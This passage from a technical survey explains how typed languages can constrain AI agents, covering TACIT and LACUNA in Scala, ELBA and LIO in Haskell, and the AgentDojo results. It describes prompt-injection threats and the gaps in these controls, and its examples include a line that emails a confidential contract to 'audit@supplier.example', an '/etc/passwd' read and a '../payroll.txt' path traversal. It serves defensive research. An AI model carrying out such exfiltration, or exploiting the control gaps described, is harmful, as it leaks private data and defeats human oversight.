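It's easy to see that this loop finishes, because the sum of the two numbers falls on every pass, but that argument isn't in the program. In a language with only bounded loops, the programmer has to put it there, for example by replacing the first line with `for _ in range(m + n)` and doing nothing once the numbers are equal. Harper's example of a total language, Gödel's T, is stricter because each recursive call can only count down by one. He calls the resulting code "rather painful".

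In this case the bound is easy to find, but it won't always be. Blum's size theorem, from 1967, shows how bad the problem can get. Choose any total language that can define functions on whole numbers, and any computable rate of growth *B*, however steep. Then there is a function *f* that the total language can express, but for which

shortest total program for *f* > *B*(shortest general program for *f*),

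where both lengths are in symbols. Harper suggests *B*(*n*) = 2<sup>2<sup>*n*</sup></sup>, which already exceeds four billion when *n* is 5. The reason is that a program in a total language has to contain a proof that it finishes, in whatever form the language accepts, and some of these proofs are enormous. A general program can leave the proof out.

The theorem doesn't establish how often such functions come up. Harper acknowledges that they may never arise in practice, though he thinks the divisor example shows that quite natural programs can be affected. Office tasks mostly involve going through finite lists of customers, files or messages, so the length of the list limits the loop. An agent is more likely to have difficulty with searches and numerical approximations, which often continue until the answer is good enough.

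A total language also cannot express its own interpreter, so an agent confined to one could not use it to write a tool that runs other programs in the same language.

### Treating recursion as an effect

A developer can allow unbounded recursion in some places without allowing it everywhere. McBride's *Turing-Completeness Totally Free* (2015) proposes treating a recursive call as an effect. When a function needs to call itself, it issues a request and specifies how to use the result. Software outside the function then determines how to handle the request, much as Monty's host determines what happens when a program tries to read a file.

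For example, the accounts agent might define a customer's owner as the customer itself if it has no parent, and otherwise as the owner of its parent. Under McBride's scheme, the second case becomes a request for the parent's owner. The definition itself is finite and always finishes, because it describes only one step of the search. The host can then handle the requests in several ways:

- **Limited fuel:** The host supplies a fixed amount of fuel and uses one unit for each recursive call. With 100 units, it would easily find an owner four companies up. If two companies were each recorded as the other's parent, the fuel would run out and the search would return no result.
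- **Regular pauses:** The program pauses at each recursive call, and the host chooses whether to let it continue. The search may go on forever, but only with the host's continuing consent.
- **Proof:** If someone proves that the search finishes for every possible input, the host can run it without any limit.

A program's type shows whether it is guaranteed to return a result. An ordinary total function from customers to companies always returns a company. A function that uses general recursion gives only a computation that might return one, so any code that uses it has to allow for failure. McBride concludes that total languages can do everything general ones can, and that the difference lies "in what you can promise".

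This makes non-termination something a program needs permission to do, rather than something the language can't compute. For example, a developer could let an agent's main program recurse freely under a time limit while requiring every policy check to finish. Fuel, which limits the number of recursive calls, only roughly limits time, because a single step between two calls could take hours.

McBride worked in Agda, a total language used mainly for computer-checked proofs. *Data.Recursion.Free* offers programmers a version of his technique in Idris, a related language. He admits that recursive functions look ugly when written this way. Languages with built-in support for effects could automatically translate ordinary recursive code into requests, so programmers wouldn't have to write the requests themselves. This would also suit models trained on ordinary code.

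## How can tracked capabilities limit a general-purpose program?

A checker can also allow unrestricted loops and recursion and examine only what each part of a program can do. Odersky and colleagues built TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types) this way, with the agent writing its programs in Scala 3, a general-purpose language. Before a program runs, the Scala compiler determines which capabilities each function could use.

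TACIT connects to agents through MCP, so it works with existing ones such as Claude Code. The agent submits a program as text. If the compiler rejects it, the agent gets the error messages and can try again. If the compiler accepts it, the program runs, but it can reach files, commands and the network only through TACIT's library. An agent that also had an ordinary shell could bypass these limits, so the project's GitHub page, lampepfl's *TACIT*, recommends turning off the agent's built-in tools.

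### How a type shows what a function can do

Suppose a program holds `f`, a capability for writing to one file, and defines two functions:

```scala
val shorten = (text: String) => text.take(100)
val save    = (text: String) => f.write(text)
```

The compiler gives them these types:

```scala
shorten: String -> String
save:    String ->{f} Unit
```

`Unit` means that `save` returns no useful value. The braces contain a function's capture set, which lists the capabilities it holds. `shorten` holds none, so it is pure. The model doesn't have to write these types, because the compiler infers them. A function that called `save` would also depend on `f`, even if it never mentioned `f`, and its type would show that. In the Python accounts program, the helper `notice_period` could have sent a contract somewhere without any sign of it, but in this system its type would show the capability it needed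 to do so.

A capture set covers every capability a function might use, even if the function never uses it. If `save` wrote to the file only one day a week, its type would be the same. The compiler therefore never has to predict what a program will do, but it rejects some harmless programs.

Developers limit a program through the types of the functions they supply. A parameter of type `String -> String` accepts only pure functions, while one of type `String => String` accepts any function from strings to strings.

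*Capturing Types* (2023) sets out the theory and proves, for a small core language, that a value's capture set always includes everything the value captures when the program runs. TACIT uses a much larger part of Scala, and Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that a further proof would be needed to show that the guarantees hold for this part.

### Three requirements

Odersky and colleagues say that a language for agents needs three properties:

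- **Capability safety:** A program can't forge a capability or conceal that it holds one.
- **Capability completeness:** Every effect that matters for safety requires a capability, except for a few that other software can contain while the program runs.
- **Local purity:** A developer can demand that one part of a program use only certain capabilities, or none at all.

Local purity depends on types that record which capabilities a function has captured. Older capability languages such as Joe-E control which code holds a capability, but their types don't record what a function has captured. Local purity applies only where the developer asks for it, so a program can send email in one line and process a contract under strict limits in the next.

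### The contract step in Scala

TACIT puts confidential data in a wrapper called `Classified`. Its most important operation is `map`:

```scala
class Classified[T]:
  def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

`map` applies a function to the wrapped contents and wraps the result. The thin arrow means the function must be pure. Another operation combines two wrapped values, which lets a program compare two contracts. Opening the wrapper requires a separate capability, which the agent doesn't have.

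For the accounts agent, a developer might supply a `mail` capability with two operations. `mail.send` accepts any address and an ordinary string. `mail.toManager` accepts a customer number and a wrapped string, looks up the account manager's address, and opens the wrapper only to send the contents there. The compiler would accept this version of the contract step:

```scala
val contract = readClassified(s"/contracts/${c.id}.txt")
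val notice   = contract.map(text => noticePeriod(text))
mail.toManager(c.id, notice)
```

Here `noticePeriod` only searches the text, so the function passed to `map` has the required type, `String -> String`. The result is a wrapped string, which `mail.toManager` accepts.

If a hostile instruction reached the model, it might write this instead:

```scala
contract.map(text => mail.send("audit@supplier.example", text))
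```

This function uses `mail`, so its type is `String ->{mail} Unit`, but `map` requires `String -> Unit`. The compiler therefore rejects the program before it reads any contract. The compiler would also reject a call to `mail.send` with the correct manager's address, because the function would still capture `mail`.

Other ways of getting the text out fail too:

- **Passing the wrapper to `mail.send`:** The operation requires an ordinary string, and `contract` isn't one.
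- **Converting the wrapper to a string:** This is allowed, but it produces only `Classified(****)`.
- **Copying the text to a variable outside `map`:** Scala treats a variable that can change as a capability, so the function that does the copying isn't pure.
- **Reversing or encoding the text:** The result is another wrapped string.

The wrapper's one weakness for the accounts policy is that its type doesn't record whose contract it contains. A program that passed Acme's notice period to `mail.toManager` with another customer's number would still compile. CaMeL's labels can list who may read each value. A developer could add something similar here by storing the customer in the wrapper and having `mail.toManager` check it. Odersky and colleagues consider the library the natural place for run-time checks of this kind, but leave them to future work.

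The compiler also relies on the library to declare its effects. If `mail.send` didn't require a capability, the compiler would treat the hostile function as pure. Odersky and colleagues may have left such a gap when they adapted AgentDojo's banking tasks. The published type of their `sendMoney` function lists no capability, and they tell the model in its instructions that side effects inside `map` run immediately.

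### Capabilities that expire

A program obtains access to files by calling `requestFileSystem` with the name of a folder and a block of code. The access should last only until the block ends. A program might try to keep it for longer by returning a function that reads a file later:

```scala
val later = requestFileSystem("/reports"): fs =>
  () => fs.access("june.txt").read()
later()
```

The compiler rejects this program for the following reasons:

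1. `fs` is a capability, and the returned function uses it, so the function's type is `() ->{fs} String`.
2. The variable `later` is outside the block, so its type can mention only names that exist there.
3. `fs` exists only inside the block, so no valid type for `later` can include it.

Storing the function in an outside variable fails for the same reason. The program can still return the text of the report, because a string holds no capabilities.

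Scala's *Capture Checking Basics* gives a subtler example of a program that squares the numbers in a list and writes each one to a log file. With an ordinary list, all the writing happens before the file closes, so the compiler accepts the program. A lazy list calculates each item only when the program uses it, which might be after the file has closed, so the compiler rejects that version.

TACIT handles network access and external commands in the same way, with a list of permitted hosts or commands for each block. A program may calculate a file name while it runs, so the library checks only then that the file is in the permitted folder, and raises an error if it isn't. The compiler also can't control what an external command does once it starts.

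### The six restrictions of safe mode

Ordinary Scala has features that could make the compiler lose track of a capability. Safe mode is a subset of the language without them. Mazur, in *Scala 3.8.3 is now available!*, announced it as an experimental feature for code written by agents or other untrusted authors. It imposes six restrictions:

1. **No unchecked casts or pattern matches.** A cast tells the compiler to treat a value as if it had a different type, so a program could use one to pass off `save` as a pure function.
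2. **No use of the `caps.unsafe` module.** Its features let programmers bypass capability tracking.
3. **No `@unchecked` annotations.** These switch off particular compiler checks.
4. **No run-time reflection.** Reflection finds and calls code by name while the program runs, where the compiler can't follow it.
5. **Capture checking must be on.** This includes tracking every change to a variable. TACIT also turns on checks for missing values.
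6. **No global objects or functions unless their own code is safe.** Otherwise a library call could have an effect that appears in no type.

According to lampepfl, TACIT currently enforces this subset with a validator that searches each program for forbidden text patterns, and its developers plan to switch to the compiler's safe mode.

The last restriction removes almost every effect. VirtusLab, a software company that works on Scala, points out that a program in safe mode can't even print its own result without a trusted library. Developers can mark library code `@assumeSafe`, which lets agents call it even though the compiler hasn't checked it under safe mode. For example, Scala's *Safe Mode* describes an object called `CheckedMailer`, whose `sendMail` function shows the user each email and sends it only if the user agrees. Agents can't mark their own code this way, and developers have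 to make sure that the code they mark is safe to call.

Safe mode permits exceptions, the errors that interrupt a program, because almost any code can cause one by dividing by zero or running out of memory. But a function inside `map` could raise an exception with the whole contract as its message, so TACIT catches exceptions and hides their contents. This makes mistakes hard to notice, because the agent's code appears to have worked while the user gets a blank result. Odersky and colleagues tell the model to return a message such as "No matching file found" instead of raising an exception.

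### Two output channels and a second model

Anything an ordinary code action prints goes back to the model, which is why line F of the Python program was dangerous. TACIT has a normal output channel, which goes to the agent's model, and a secure one, which goes only to the user's screen. Ordinary values appear on both. When a program prints a wrapped contract, the user sees the text, but the model receives only `Classified(****)`.

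This continues to work over a long conversation. Suppose the user has received a summary of a contract and asks how long it is. The agent can calculate the length with `map` and print it for the user without ever seeing the number itself. Odersky and colleagues contrast this with run-time labels, which disappear once a value enters a model's conversation as plain text. That criticism is fair for some systems, but LLMbda avoids the problem by labelling the conversation as well.

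A model that can't read a contract can't summarise it or interpret odd wording. TACIT therefore gives programs a `chat` function, which calls a second model that the company trusts with the data, perhaps one running on the company's own computers. For example, `chat("What is the notice period?", contract)` returns a wrapped answer.

CaMeL also divides the work between two models, but it relies on its planning model having read no untrusted data. Odersky and colleagues assume that the main model may already be following an attacker's instructions.

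The compiler treats `chat` as pure but cannot verify that it is, so it relies on the developer to make sure. If the trusted model remembered earlier requests, an agent could show it a wrapped contract and then ask for the contract's text in an ordinary message. The reply would be an ordinary string, which the agent could send anywhere. The developer has to ensure that the trusted model keeps no memory and has no tools.

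Odersky and colleagues argue that prompt injection does real harm only by sending private data to the wrong place or by triggering a capability the agent was never granted. This seems too narrow. A supplier's email that nobody had classified could get the accounts agent to send every customer a false final demand, using only the `mail` capability it needs for its job. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a follow-up by largely the same researchers, concedes that the type checker doesn't stop an attacker who gets the model to misuse a capability it legitimately holds.

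The developer could classify the emails too, but VirtusLab warns that an agent is useful largely because it can read and understand what people send it. Classifying more data reduces what the agent can do.

### Why recursion and higher-order functions can stay

CaMeL's subset of Python doesn't let the model define functions. TACIT lets it define them, make them recursive, and pass them to other functions. The accounts agent could search for an ultimate owner like this:

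```scala
def owner(id: String): String =
  parent.get(id) match
    case Some(p) => owner(p)
    case None    => id
```

The compiler verifies that `owner` uses no capabilities without calculating how many times the function will call itself. It doesn't check that the search ends.

Functions that take other functions as inputs are harder to check. Suppose the agent writes a function `retry` that runs any action it is given up to three times. What `retry` can do depends entirely on the action. Without annotations, a checker would have to find every action that could reach `retry`, even through several other functions. Odersky and colleagues note that a precise analysis of this kind can take exponential time in the worst case.

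Capture types let the compiler check a function separately from the calls to it. The compiler first checks the code of `retry` against its declared type, which lets the action use any capability. It then checks each call to `retry`. If a call passes in an action that writes to `f`, the compiler adds `f` to the capabilities that call needs. It doesn't have to recheck the code of `retry` unless that code changes.

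Other systems for tracking effects can also check functions one at a time, but they often need more notation. The standard example in *Capturing Types* is `map`, which applies a function to every item in an ordinary list. Under a traditional effect system, the type of `map` must include the effects of the supplied function, and the same is true of Scala's many similar functions. With capture sets, `map` keeps the type it had before Scala tracked capabilities.

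LLMbda also combines unlimited recursion with control over data, but it enforces its labels while the program runs rather than at compile time. Capture checking has the advantage of finding violations before the program runs, and it adds no checks to each step.

### Letting the model write the agent's own control flow

With TACIT, the model writes programs, but separate software still decides when to call the model and what to show it. In LACUNA, the model can write that part too. The system adds one function to Scala, `agent[T](task)`, which asks a model for code that produces a value of type `T`. A developer could write:

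```scala
var balance = 100
val left: Int = agent("subtract 50 and return the new balance")
```

When the program reaches the second line, LACUNA sends the model the task, the required type, the surrounding code and a list of the available variables. In one of Zhao and colleagues' examples, the model replies with this code:

```scala
balance -= 50
s"remaining: $balance"
```

LACUNA inserts the reply into the surrounding program and runs the ordinary Scala compiler on the result. The last line produces text where the program needs a whole number, so the compiler rejects the entire reply. The subtraction never runs, and `balance` stays at 100. LACUNA then sends the compiler's errors to the model for another attempt. If the first line had already run, as it would have in Python, the second attempt might have subtracted 50 again.

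The model's code can call `agent`. To write a report on several topics, the model might write a loop that makes one call per topic in parallel, then a call to combine the findings. It could also take a few steps towards an answer and end with another call for the same task, which produces the usual agent loop of acting, reading the result and acting again. The model therefore decides how many helpers to use and what each one does. The types don't limit how deeply these calls can nest, so the developer has to set a maximum.

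Each call can use only the capabilities available where it appears in the code. For example, a call can read files only inside a block that grants file access. To give a helper fewer capabilities, a program can call it from a separate function, where the helper can use only that function's inputs and whatever is available throughout the program.

LACUNA can also deal with oddly worded contracts better than TACIT alone. In TACIT, the main model has to write the function for `map` without seeing the contract. In LACUNA, that function can ask a trusted local model to write code once the text is available:

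```scala
val notice = contract.map { text =>
  local.agent[Int]("Find the notice period in days")
}
```

The local model can read `text` and write a search suited to that contract. A hidden instruction might cause it to write code that emails the text to a stranger, but `map` requires a pure function, so the compiler would reject that code.

The all-or-nothing rule applies to each reply separately and covers only errors that the compiler can find. Suppose the model writes a program that sends ten emails and then calls `agent` for the next step. If the compiler rejects every attempt at that step, the ten emails have still gone out. Code that passes the check can also fail partway through, for instance if a server is down. As Zhao and colleagues point out, code with the right type can still do the wrong thing, so a reply that subtracted 60 from the balance would pass the check.

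### Why Scala, and what counts against it

Odersky and colleagues chose Scala because they consider it the only language ready for production use whose types track capabilities. They discuss four alternatives:

- **Another mainstream language:** Someone would have to add capability tracking and a way to enforce purity, starting from a weaker base.
- **Haskell:** Its types already separate pure code from code with effects, but it has no built-in capabilities of this kind, so developers would have to represent them with more elaborate types.
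- **E or Joe-E:** These languages enforce capabilities only while a program runs. To guarantee local purity, they would need capture types or a rule that functions can never hold on to a capability.
- **A new language:** People must be able to read and edit what agents write, and models learn from human examples. A new language would take a large investment to match the support that popular ones have.

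Capture checking is still experimental, which casts some doubt on the claim that Scala is ready for production. Scala's *Tracked Capabilities Overview* calls it "quite mature" and expects it to become stable soon, while *Capture Checking Basics* calls it "highly experimental and unstable". The latest long-term version of Scala made one feature stable, but not capture checking (Mazur, *Scala 3.9 LTS released!*). Lampepfl warns that TACIT is built on nightly versions of the compiler, whose behaviour may change, so a company that relied on TACIT would have to expect some maintenance.

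Capture checking is also rare in the code that models learn from. Odersky and colleagues reply that the annotations are light and the patterns repetitive, so a model can learn them from instructions and a few examples. In their tests, agents using TACIT did about as well as agents making tool calls, though those using LACUNA did worse. Some recurring errors were unrelated to capabilities. For example, models would write `$50` inside a string, where a dollar sign in Scala marks the start of a variable. Zhao and colleagues suspect that LACUNA's difficulty is partly due to models' limited experience with Scala.

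Developers have a moderate amount of work to do. TACIT's reusable library is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and each new set of tools needs up to a few hundred more, mostly descriptions of data and functions that a tool-calling agent would need in another form anyway. Developers can also now use ATC, a ready-made coding agent built on TACIT. According to Glama's *TACIT*, ATC denies every permission by default, and users can grant one temporarily or for a whole session.

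## How can effect types limit a general-purpose program?

Scala's capture checking records which capabilities each function holds, whereas Haskell's types record what kind of effects a whole computation may have. Zhou and colleagues build on this in language-based agent control. The model and the developer both write Haskell, and the developer states policies as types. Their implementation is ELBA, which they originally named TypeGuard. It gives the developer one new function:

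```haskell
agent :: Defs -> Prompt -> t
```

`Defs` lists the types and functions the model may use, `Prompt` describes the task, and `t` stands for whatever type the surrounding program needs. When a running program reaches a call to `agent`, ELBA does the following:

1. It sends the model the task, the definitions and the required type, and the model writes a Haskell program.
2. It type-checks the program. If the type is wrong, the model gets the error message and tries again.
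3. It runs the program and uses the result as the value of the call.

This is close to LACUNA's `agent[T](task)`. In both systems, the required type also specifies what the model should produce. For example, a developer might write only the ambiguous task "parse this". If the program then sorts the results with a function that compares dates, Haskell infers that each call must return a date, and ELBA passes that type to the model.

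### A program that may only return a number

The calculator that rejects a request to delete the server's files needs very little code:

```haskell
calculate :: String -> Int
calculate question = agent arithmetic question
```

`Int` is the type of whole numbers. Haskell marks programs that have outside effects with `IO`, so a program that deletes the files and then returns the factorial of 5 has type `IO Int`, which doesn't match `Int`. The model can still use any loop or recursive function.

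Pure Haskell code of type `Int` can still throw an exception by dividing by zero, although Zhou and colleagues say that the type also rules out exceptions. Such code can run forever too, and a company that offered this calculator to the public would still need limits on time and memory.

### The bibliography in three versions

Most agents need some effects. The bibliography agent has to search DBLP and write to a file, and every entry it writes must come from DBLP. Suppose a user asks for the earliest paper on a topic. With a code interpreter, the model could write this program, shown in Haskell notation:

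```haskell
do dois    <- dblpSearch "capability security"
   entries <- mapM dblpFetchBib dois
   appendToBibFile (earliest entries)
```

The program searches for papers, fetches their entries and adds the earliest one to the file. But an interpreter would also run `writeFile "refs.bib" fake`, where `fake` is an entry the model made up.

The version with fixed tools replaces only `appendToBibFile`, using `fetchAndAppend` instead, which takes a DOI and writes that paper's entry in one step. This rules out false entries, but the model has to compare the fetched entries itself.

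ELBA keeps the program above and gives the library's functions these types:

```haskell
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

`BibIO` is a new effect type that the developer defines. Only the library's functions produce it, and the developer requires the model's program to have type `BibIO ()`, where `()` means that it returns nothing useful. `Trusted` is a wrapper around an entry. The function that creates the wrapper, called its constructor, is hidden inside the library, so a program can get a wrapped entry only from `dblpFetchBib`. The program may combine the three functions with any pure code, including `earliest`, but the obvious ways to cheat fail:

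| Attempt | Why the type checker rejects it |
|---|---|
| `writeFile "refs.bib" fake` | It has type `IO ()`, not `BibIO ()` |
| `appendToBibFile fake` | `fake` is an ordinary string, not a `Trusted Bib` |
| `appendToBibFile (Trusted fake)` | The constructor `Trusted` isn't available outside the library |

The policy needs both parts. Without `BibIO`, the program could bypass `appendToBibFile`, and without `Trusted`, it could pass that function a false entry. Garby and colleagues point out that LLMbda's labels can do the same job as such tokens. The library would label DBLP's entries as trusted, and the function that writes to the file would check for the label at run time.

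These types guarantee only where an entry came from. The agent invented no citations in tests, but it could still cite a real paper unrelated to the topic. A program that does nothing also has type `BibIO ()`, so the type doesn't guarantee that the program adds any entries.

The accounts agent could use the same technique for addresses. If `mail.send` accepted only wrapped addresses, and only a lookup in the customer table could produce them, a supplier's email could not introduce a new recipient. The program could still send a contract to the wrong customer's manager, because the wrapper records where the address came from but not which contracts the recipient may read.

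### Paths that a program can only narrow

For files, ELBA has an effect type called `RIO`, for restricted input and output. Its functions don't accept file names as ordinary strings. They require a value of type `Path`, which is a capability for one folder and everything inside it. The developer's code chooses a starting folder, and the operator `//` derives narrower paths from it:

```haskell
readAcme :: Path -> RIO String
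readAcme contracts = readRIO (contracts // "acme.txt")
```

A program that called `readRIO "/etc/passwd"` would not compile, because `readRIO` doesn't accept a string as a file name. The expression `contracts // "../payroll.txt"` does compile, since the type checker doesn't examine what a string contains. When the program runs, `//` resolves the path, following any links between folders, and fails if it leads outside `contracts`.

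The *Safe Haskell* section of the manual for GHC, the main Haskell compiler, describes a simpler type with the same name. That type's functions accept any file name and check it against one policy for the whole program. With `Path`, by contrast, a program can give one function access to a single subfolder. Zhou and colleagues suggest that a similar token could represent something other than a folder, such as all the files on one branch of a code repository.

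By contrast, some coding agents decide whether to allow a shell command by comparing its text with patterns. In March 2026, a fault in Claude Code let commands joined with `&&` bypass its rules because the software checked only the first command.

### A label that rises as the program reads

ELBA uses the Haskell library LIO to control where data goes. Stefan, Mazières and colleagues (2017) describe LIO in *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions*. LIO keeps one current label, which covers everything the running program has read so far, whereas CaMeL and LLMbda label every value.

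Two rules govern the current label, written *l*<sub>cur</sub>. In these rules, *A* ⊑ *B* means that data labelled *A* may flow to a place labelled *B*, and *A* ⊔ *B* is the label that combines the restrictions of *A* and *B*.

- **Reading:** When the program reads data labelled *l*, the current label becomes *l*<sub>cur</sub> ⊔ *l*.
- **Writing:** The program may write to a place labelled *l* only if *l*<sub>cur</sub> ⊑ *l*.

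ELBA's labels record who may see the data and which sources influenced it. In an example from Zhou and colleagues, a program downloads a page from phony.com and then tries to show it to the user. The download adds phony.com to the sources in the current label. The user's screen accepts only more trusted data, so LIO raises an error.

A single label also prevents the leak through unused branches that affects CaMeL. A program has to open a labelled secret before branching on it, and opening it raises the current label. From then on the program can't write to any public place, whichever branch it takes.

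The label can rise until the program can't do anything useful, a problem known as label creep. Suppose the accounts agent reads Acme's contract, which only Lee may see, and then another customer's contract, which only Kim may see. The current label now allows only readers who may see both contracts. Neither Lee nor Kim qualifies, so the program can't email either of them.

LIO's `toLabeled` function solves this by running part of a program separately. When that part finishes, the current label returns to its earlier value, and the result comes back in a sealed wrapper with its own label. The accounts agent could find each notice period this way and pass the sealed result to a mail function that checks whether the recipient may read it. The current label would rise only if the program itself opened the wrapper.

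A developer can also set a clearance, an upper limit on the current label, so that a program can't read data above that limit. Stefan and colleagues point out that code can't leak sensitive data it can't access. This protection matters because LIO's security proofs, many of them computer-checked, don't cover what an observer could learn from how long a program runs or whether it finishes.

### Which checks happen before the program runs

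| Version | Before the program runs | While it runs |
|---|---|---|
| Calculator | The program is pure and returns a whole number | No policy checks |
| Bibliography | It uses only the library's effects and writes only wrapped entries | No policy checks |
| Files | It uses only `RIO` operations and gives each one a `Path` | Each new path stays inside the permitted folder |
| Information flow | It uses only LIO operations | Labels permit each read and write |

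In the information-flow version, the types do little more than keep the program inside LIO, and the library enforces the policy at run time. This allows more programs than a compile-time check would. Stefan and colleagues note that a compile-time check would reject a program for one insecure line that never runs, while LIO stops a program only when it is about to violate the policy. But LIO's checks, like CaMeL's, can stop a program halfway.

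ELBA prompts the model for a corrected program after a type error, when none of the program's tool calls has run, but not after a run-time error. A program can still catch an LIO error and continue, so one refused message doesn't have to end the job.

### How an agent loop arises

One call to `agent` produces one complete program, so by itself it doesn't let the model look at a result before deciding what to do next. The model can get that chance by writing a program that calls the model again. In generated code, the function for this is called `subagent`, and it takes a task and a piece of data. The bibliography agent might check one search result before it goes further:

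```haskell
do dois  <- dblpSearch "capability security"
   first <- dblpFetchBib (head dois)
   subagent "Refine the search or write the entries."
            (show first) :: BibIO ()
```

The sub-agent receives the text of the first entry and writes the next program, which may end with another call. Repeating this gives the usual agent loop, as in LACUNA. The sub-agent may use the same library functions, but it sees only the two strings, not the parent's variables or code. It has to fetch the entry from DBLP again before writing it, because text can't be turned back into a `Trusted Bib`.

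The sub-agent can't exceed its parent's policy. The parent calls it from within a `BibIO` program, so the program it writes must also have type `BibIO ()`. The parent could ask for a program of type `IO ()`, but it couldn't run that program within `BibIO`. A parent can impose a stricter policy, for instance by asking for a plain `String`, which forces the sub-agent's program to be pure.

It can also restrict a sub-agent to particular data. The parent below asks for a function and then applies it to one customer's folder:

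```haskell
let findNotice = subagent "Write a function to find the notice period."
                          "Contracts are text files."
                   :: Path -> RIO String
in findNotice (contracts // "acme")
```

The function can read only Acme's files, since `//` can't reach any others. But `RIO` permits writing as well as reading, so the function could also change those files unless the developer supplied a read-only version.

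Running a sub-agent inside `toLabeled` gives a more flexible form of CaMeL's two-model split. Zhou and colleagues describe an agent that has to summarise an outside email in a direct message, using a web address for the email that comes from untrusted input. A sub-agent inside `toLabeled` fetches the email and drafts the message. The sub-agent's label rises without raising the parent's, and the parent receives the draft sealed. In CaMeL, the quarantined model has no tools, so the planning model's program has to fetch the email.

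The parent then calls `sendDM` with a recipient and the sealed draft. This function first checks that the parent's current label is still untainted, since otherwise an attacker might have chosen the recipient. It then uses a special privilege to open the draft and send it. An attacker who wrote the email can therefore affect what the message says but not who gets it. Garby and colleagues' meeting reminder had the opposite policy: it protected the text but not the recipient. In both systems, the developer decides which parts of a message untrusted data may influence.

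### The soundness theorem

Zhou and colleagues prove that adding agents to a language doesn't weaken what its types guarantee. Let *L* be the host language, in this case Haskell, and let *L*<sub>agent</sub> be the same language with the `agent` function added. For a program *e*, let traces(*e*) be the set of all sequences of tool calls with visible effects that *e* can make. A type *t* guarantees a property *P* if

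*e* has type *t* ⟹ *P*(traces(*e*)) for every program *e* in *L*.

For the type `BibIO ()`, *P* might be "every entry written to the file came from DBLP". By the theorem, a type that guarantees a property in *L* also guarantees it in *L*<sub>agent</sub>.

The proof replaces each agent call with an ordinary function that does the same thing:

1. Every agent call has a limit *n* on how deeply further calls can nest inside it. The result is optional, because the model may fail to produce a valid program.
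2. For *n* = 0, the replacement function *a*<sub>0</sub> simply returns "nothing".
3. For a higher limit, *a*<sub>*n*+1</sub> queries the model and type-checks the reply. If the reply fails the check, it returns "nothing". Otherwise, it replaces any agent calls inside the reply with *a*<sub>*n*</sub> or a function with a lower limit, and runs the result.
4. Replacing all the agent calls in a program *e* gives a program *e*<sub>*L*</sub>, which belongs to the ordinary language *L* and has the same type as *e*.
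5. The two programs make the same tool calls. This is clear at depth 0, where both return "nothing". If it holds up to depth *n*, it also holds at *n* + 1, because both versions get the same reply from the model and any calls inside that reply have a depth of at most *n*.
6. The type guarantees *P* for *e*<sub>*L*</sub>, so *P* also holds for *e*.

The proof doesn't depend on the model's intentions or competence, so the theorem holds even if the reply is a program that an attacker dictated word for word.

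Zhou and colleagues treat the model as a function that always gives the same reply to the same prompt. They argue that randomness doesn't affect the properties they consider, and suggest storing and reusing replies where it would matter. Garby and colleagues' theorem for LLMbda covers random replies directly.

Requests to the model also don't count as effects in the proof. The `subagent` function can return a plain `Int`, so a program that type-checks as pure can still send a contract's text to whichever company hosts the model. TACIT has the same gap in its `chat` function. A developer with confidential data would therefore have to choose a model that their company trusts with it.

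### What the theorem takes for granted

The theorem depends on the host language's guarantees, so it is only as good as Haskell's type system. *Safe Haskell* (Terei, Mazières and colleagues, 2012) sets two conditions for confining untrusted code by its types. The type system must have no loopholes, and programs must not be able to access what a library hides. Ordinary Haskell meets neither condition. Its `unsafePerformIO` function can make any effect look like a pure value, so a program of type `Int` could delete files. Template Haskell, a feature for generating code during compilation, can access hidden constructors such as `Trusted`.

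Safe Haskell is a subset of the language without these features. A program in it may import a module only if the compiler has checked that module under the same rules or the module's author has vouched for it by marking it "Trustworthy". LIO's core is marked Trustworthy, according to Hackage's *LIO.Core*. The subset doesn't restrict effects by itself, and Terei and colleagues note that a program in it can delete all of a user's files. Safe Haskell only makes types reliable enough for a developer to build restrictions like `BibIO` on top of them.

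Zhou and colleagues say that Safe Haskell closed the `unsafePerformIO` loophole long ago. Some Haskell developers have less confidence in Safe Haskell as a whole. In 2021, Richard, a GHC developer, wrote to a Haskell mailing list that it was unclear which of Safe Haskell's guarantees the compiler delivered. He pointed to a bug that let programs convert a value of one type into another without permission, and considered removing Safe Haskell altogether. In a forum discussion the following year, *Deprecating Safe Haskell, or heavily investing in it?*, several developers supported dropping or redesigning it. One problem they raised was that GHC's developers have to remember to forbid each unsafe new feature, and had allowed one, `DerivingVia`, until May 2021.

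The current manual still includes Safe Haskell. ELBA's design should make some of these weaknesses harder to exploit, because the model has to supply a single expression, and a Haskell expression can't declare new types, which `DerivingVia` requires. It is still safest to run ELBA inside a process sandbox as well. GHC's documentation recommends a sandbox even for compiling untrusted code, since some compiler settings can start other programs before the code runs.

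The guarantee also covers only Haskell code. Zhou and colleagues stress that the developer's own code, including the part that handles retries, must be in Haskell too. As with TACIT, the types would not restrict a separate shell, nor would they restrict a tool that passes work to a Python program. ELBA's current types also do not limit running time or memory, though Zhou and colleagues suggest that more elaborate ones could.

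Finally, the types have to express what the developer meant. If `dblpFetchBib` accepted any web address instead of a DOI, an attacker could put a false entry online and the library would wrap it as `Trusted`. The agent could then add it to the bibliography without breaking any rule the type checker enforces.

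## What do the restrictions cost in completed tasks, and what do they stop?

An agent may complete fewer tasks in a restricted language even if the developer forbids nothing. The model may write the language poorly, or the compiler may reject so many of its programs that the agent never finishes. A policy reduces the number of completed tasks when it blocks correct programs that do what the user asked. Researchers can separate the two effects by running the same agent on the same tasks with its policies off and then on.

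Many of the experiments use the AgentDojo benchmark. *AgentDojo* (2024), the paper that introduced it, reports that its tasks take up to 18 tool calls. Peters-Gill and colleagues list 97 ordinary tasks (40 office, 21 Slack, 16 banking and 20 travel) and 35 attacker goals. Pairing each task with every goal in the same group gives 949 attack trials. In each trial, the benchmark hides an instruction in data returned by one of the agent's tools, then scores whether the agent completed the user's task and whether the attacker succeeded.

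### What the language costs without a policy

Odersky and colleagues compared TACIT with ordinary tool calling on τ²-bench, in which an agent helps simulated customers change flights or return goods. Each model attempted every task ten times with each method.

| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, TACIT | Retail, tool calls | Retail, TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
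| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

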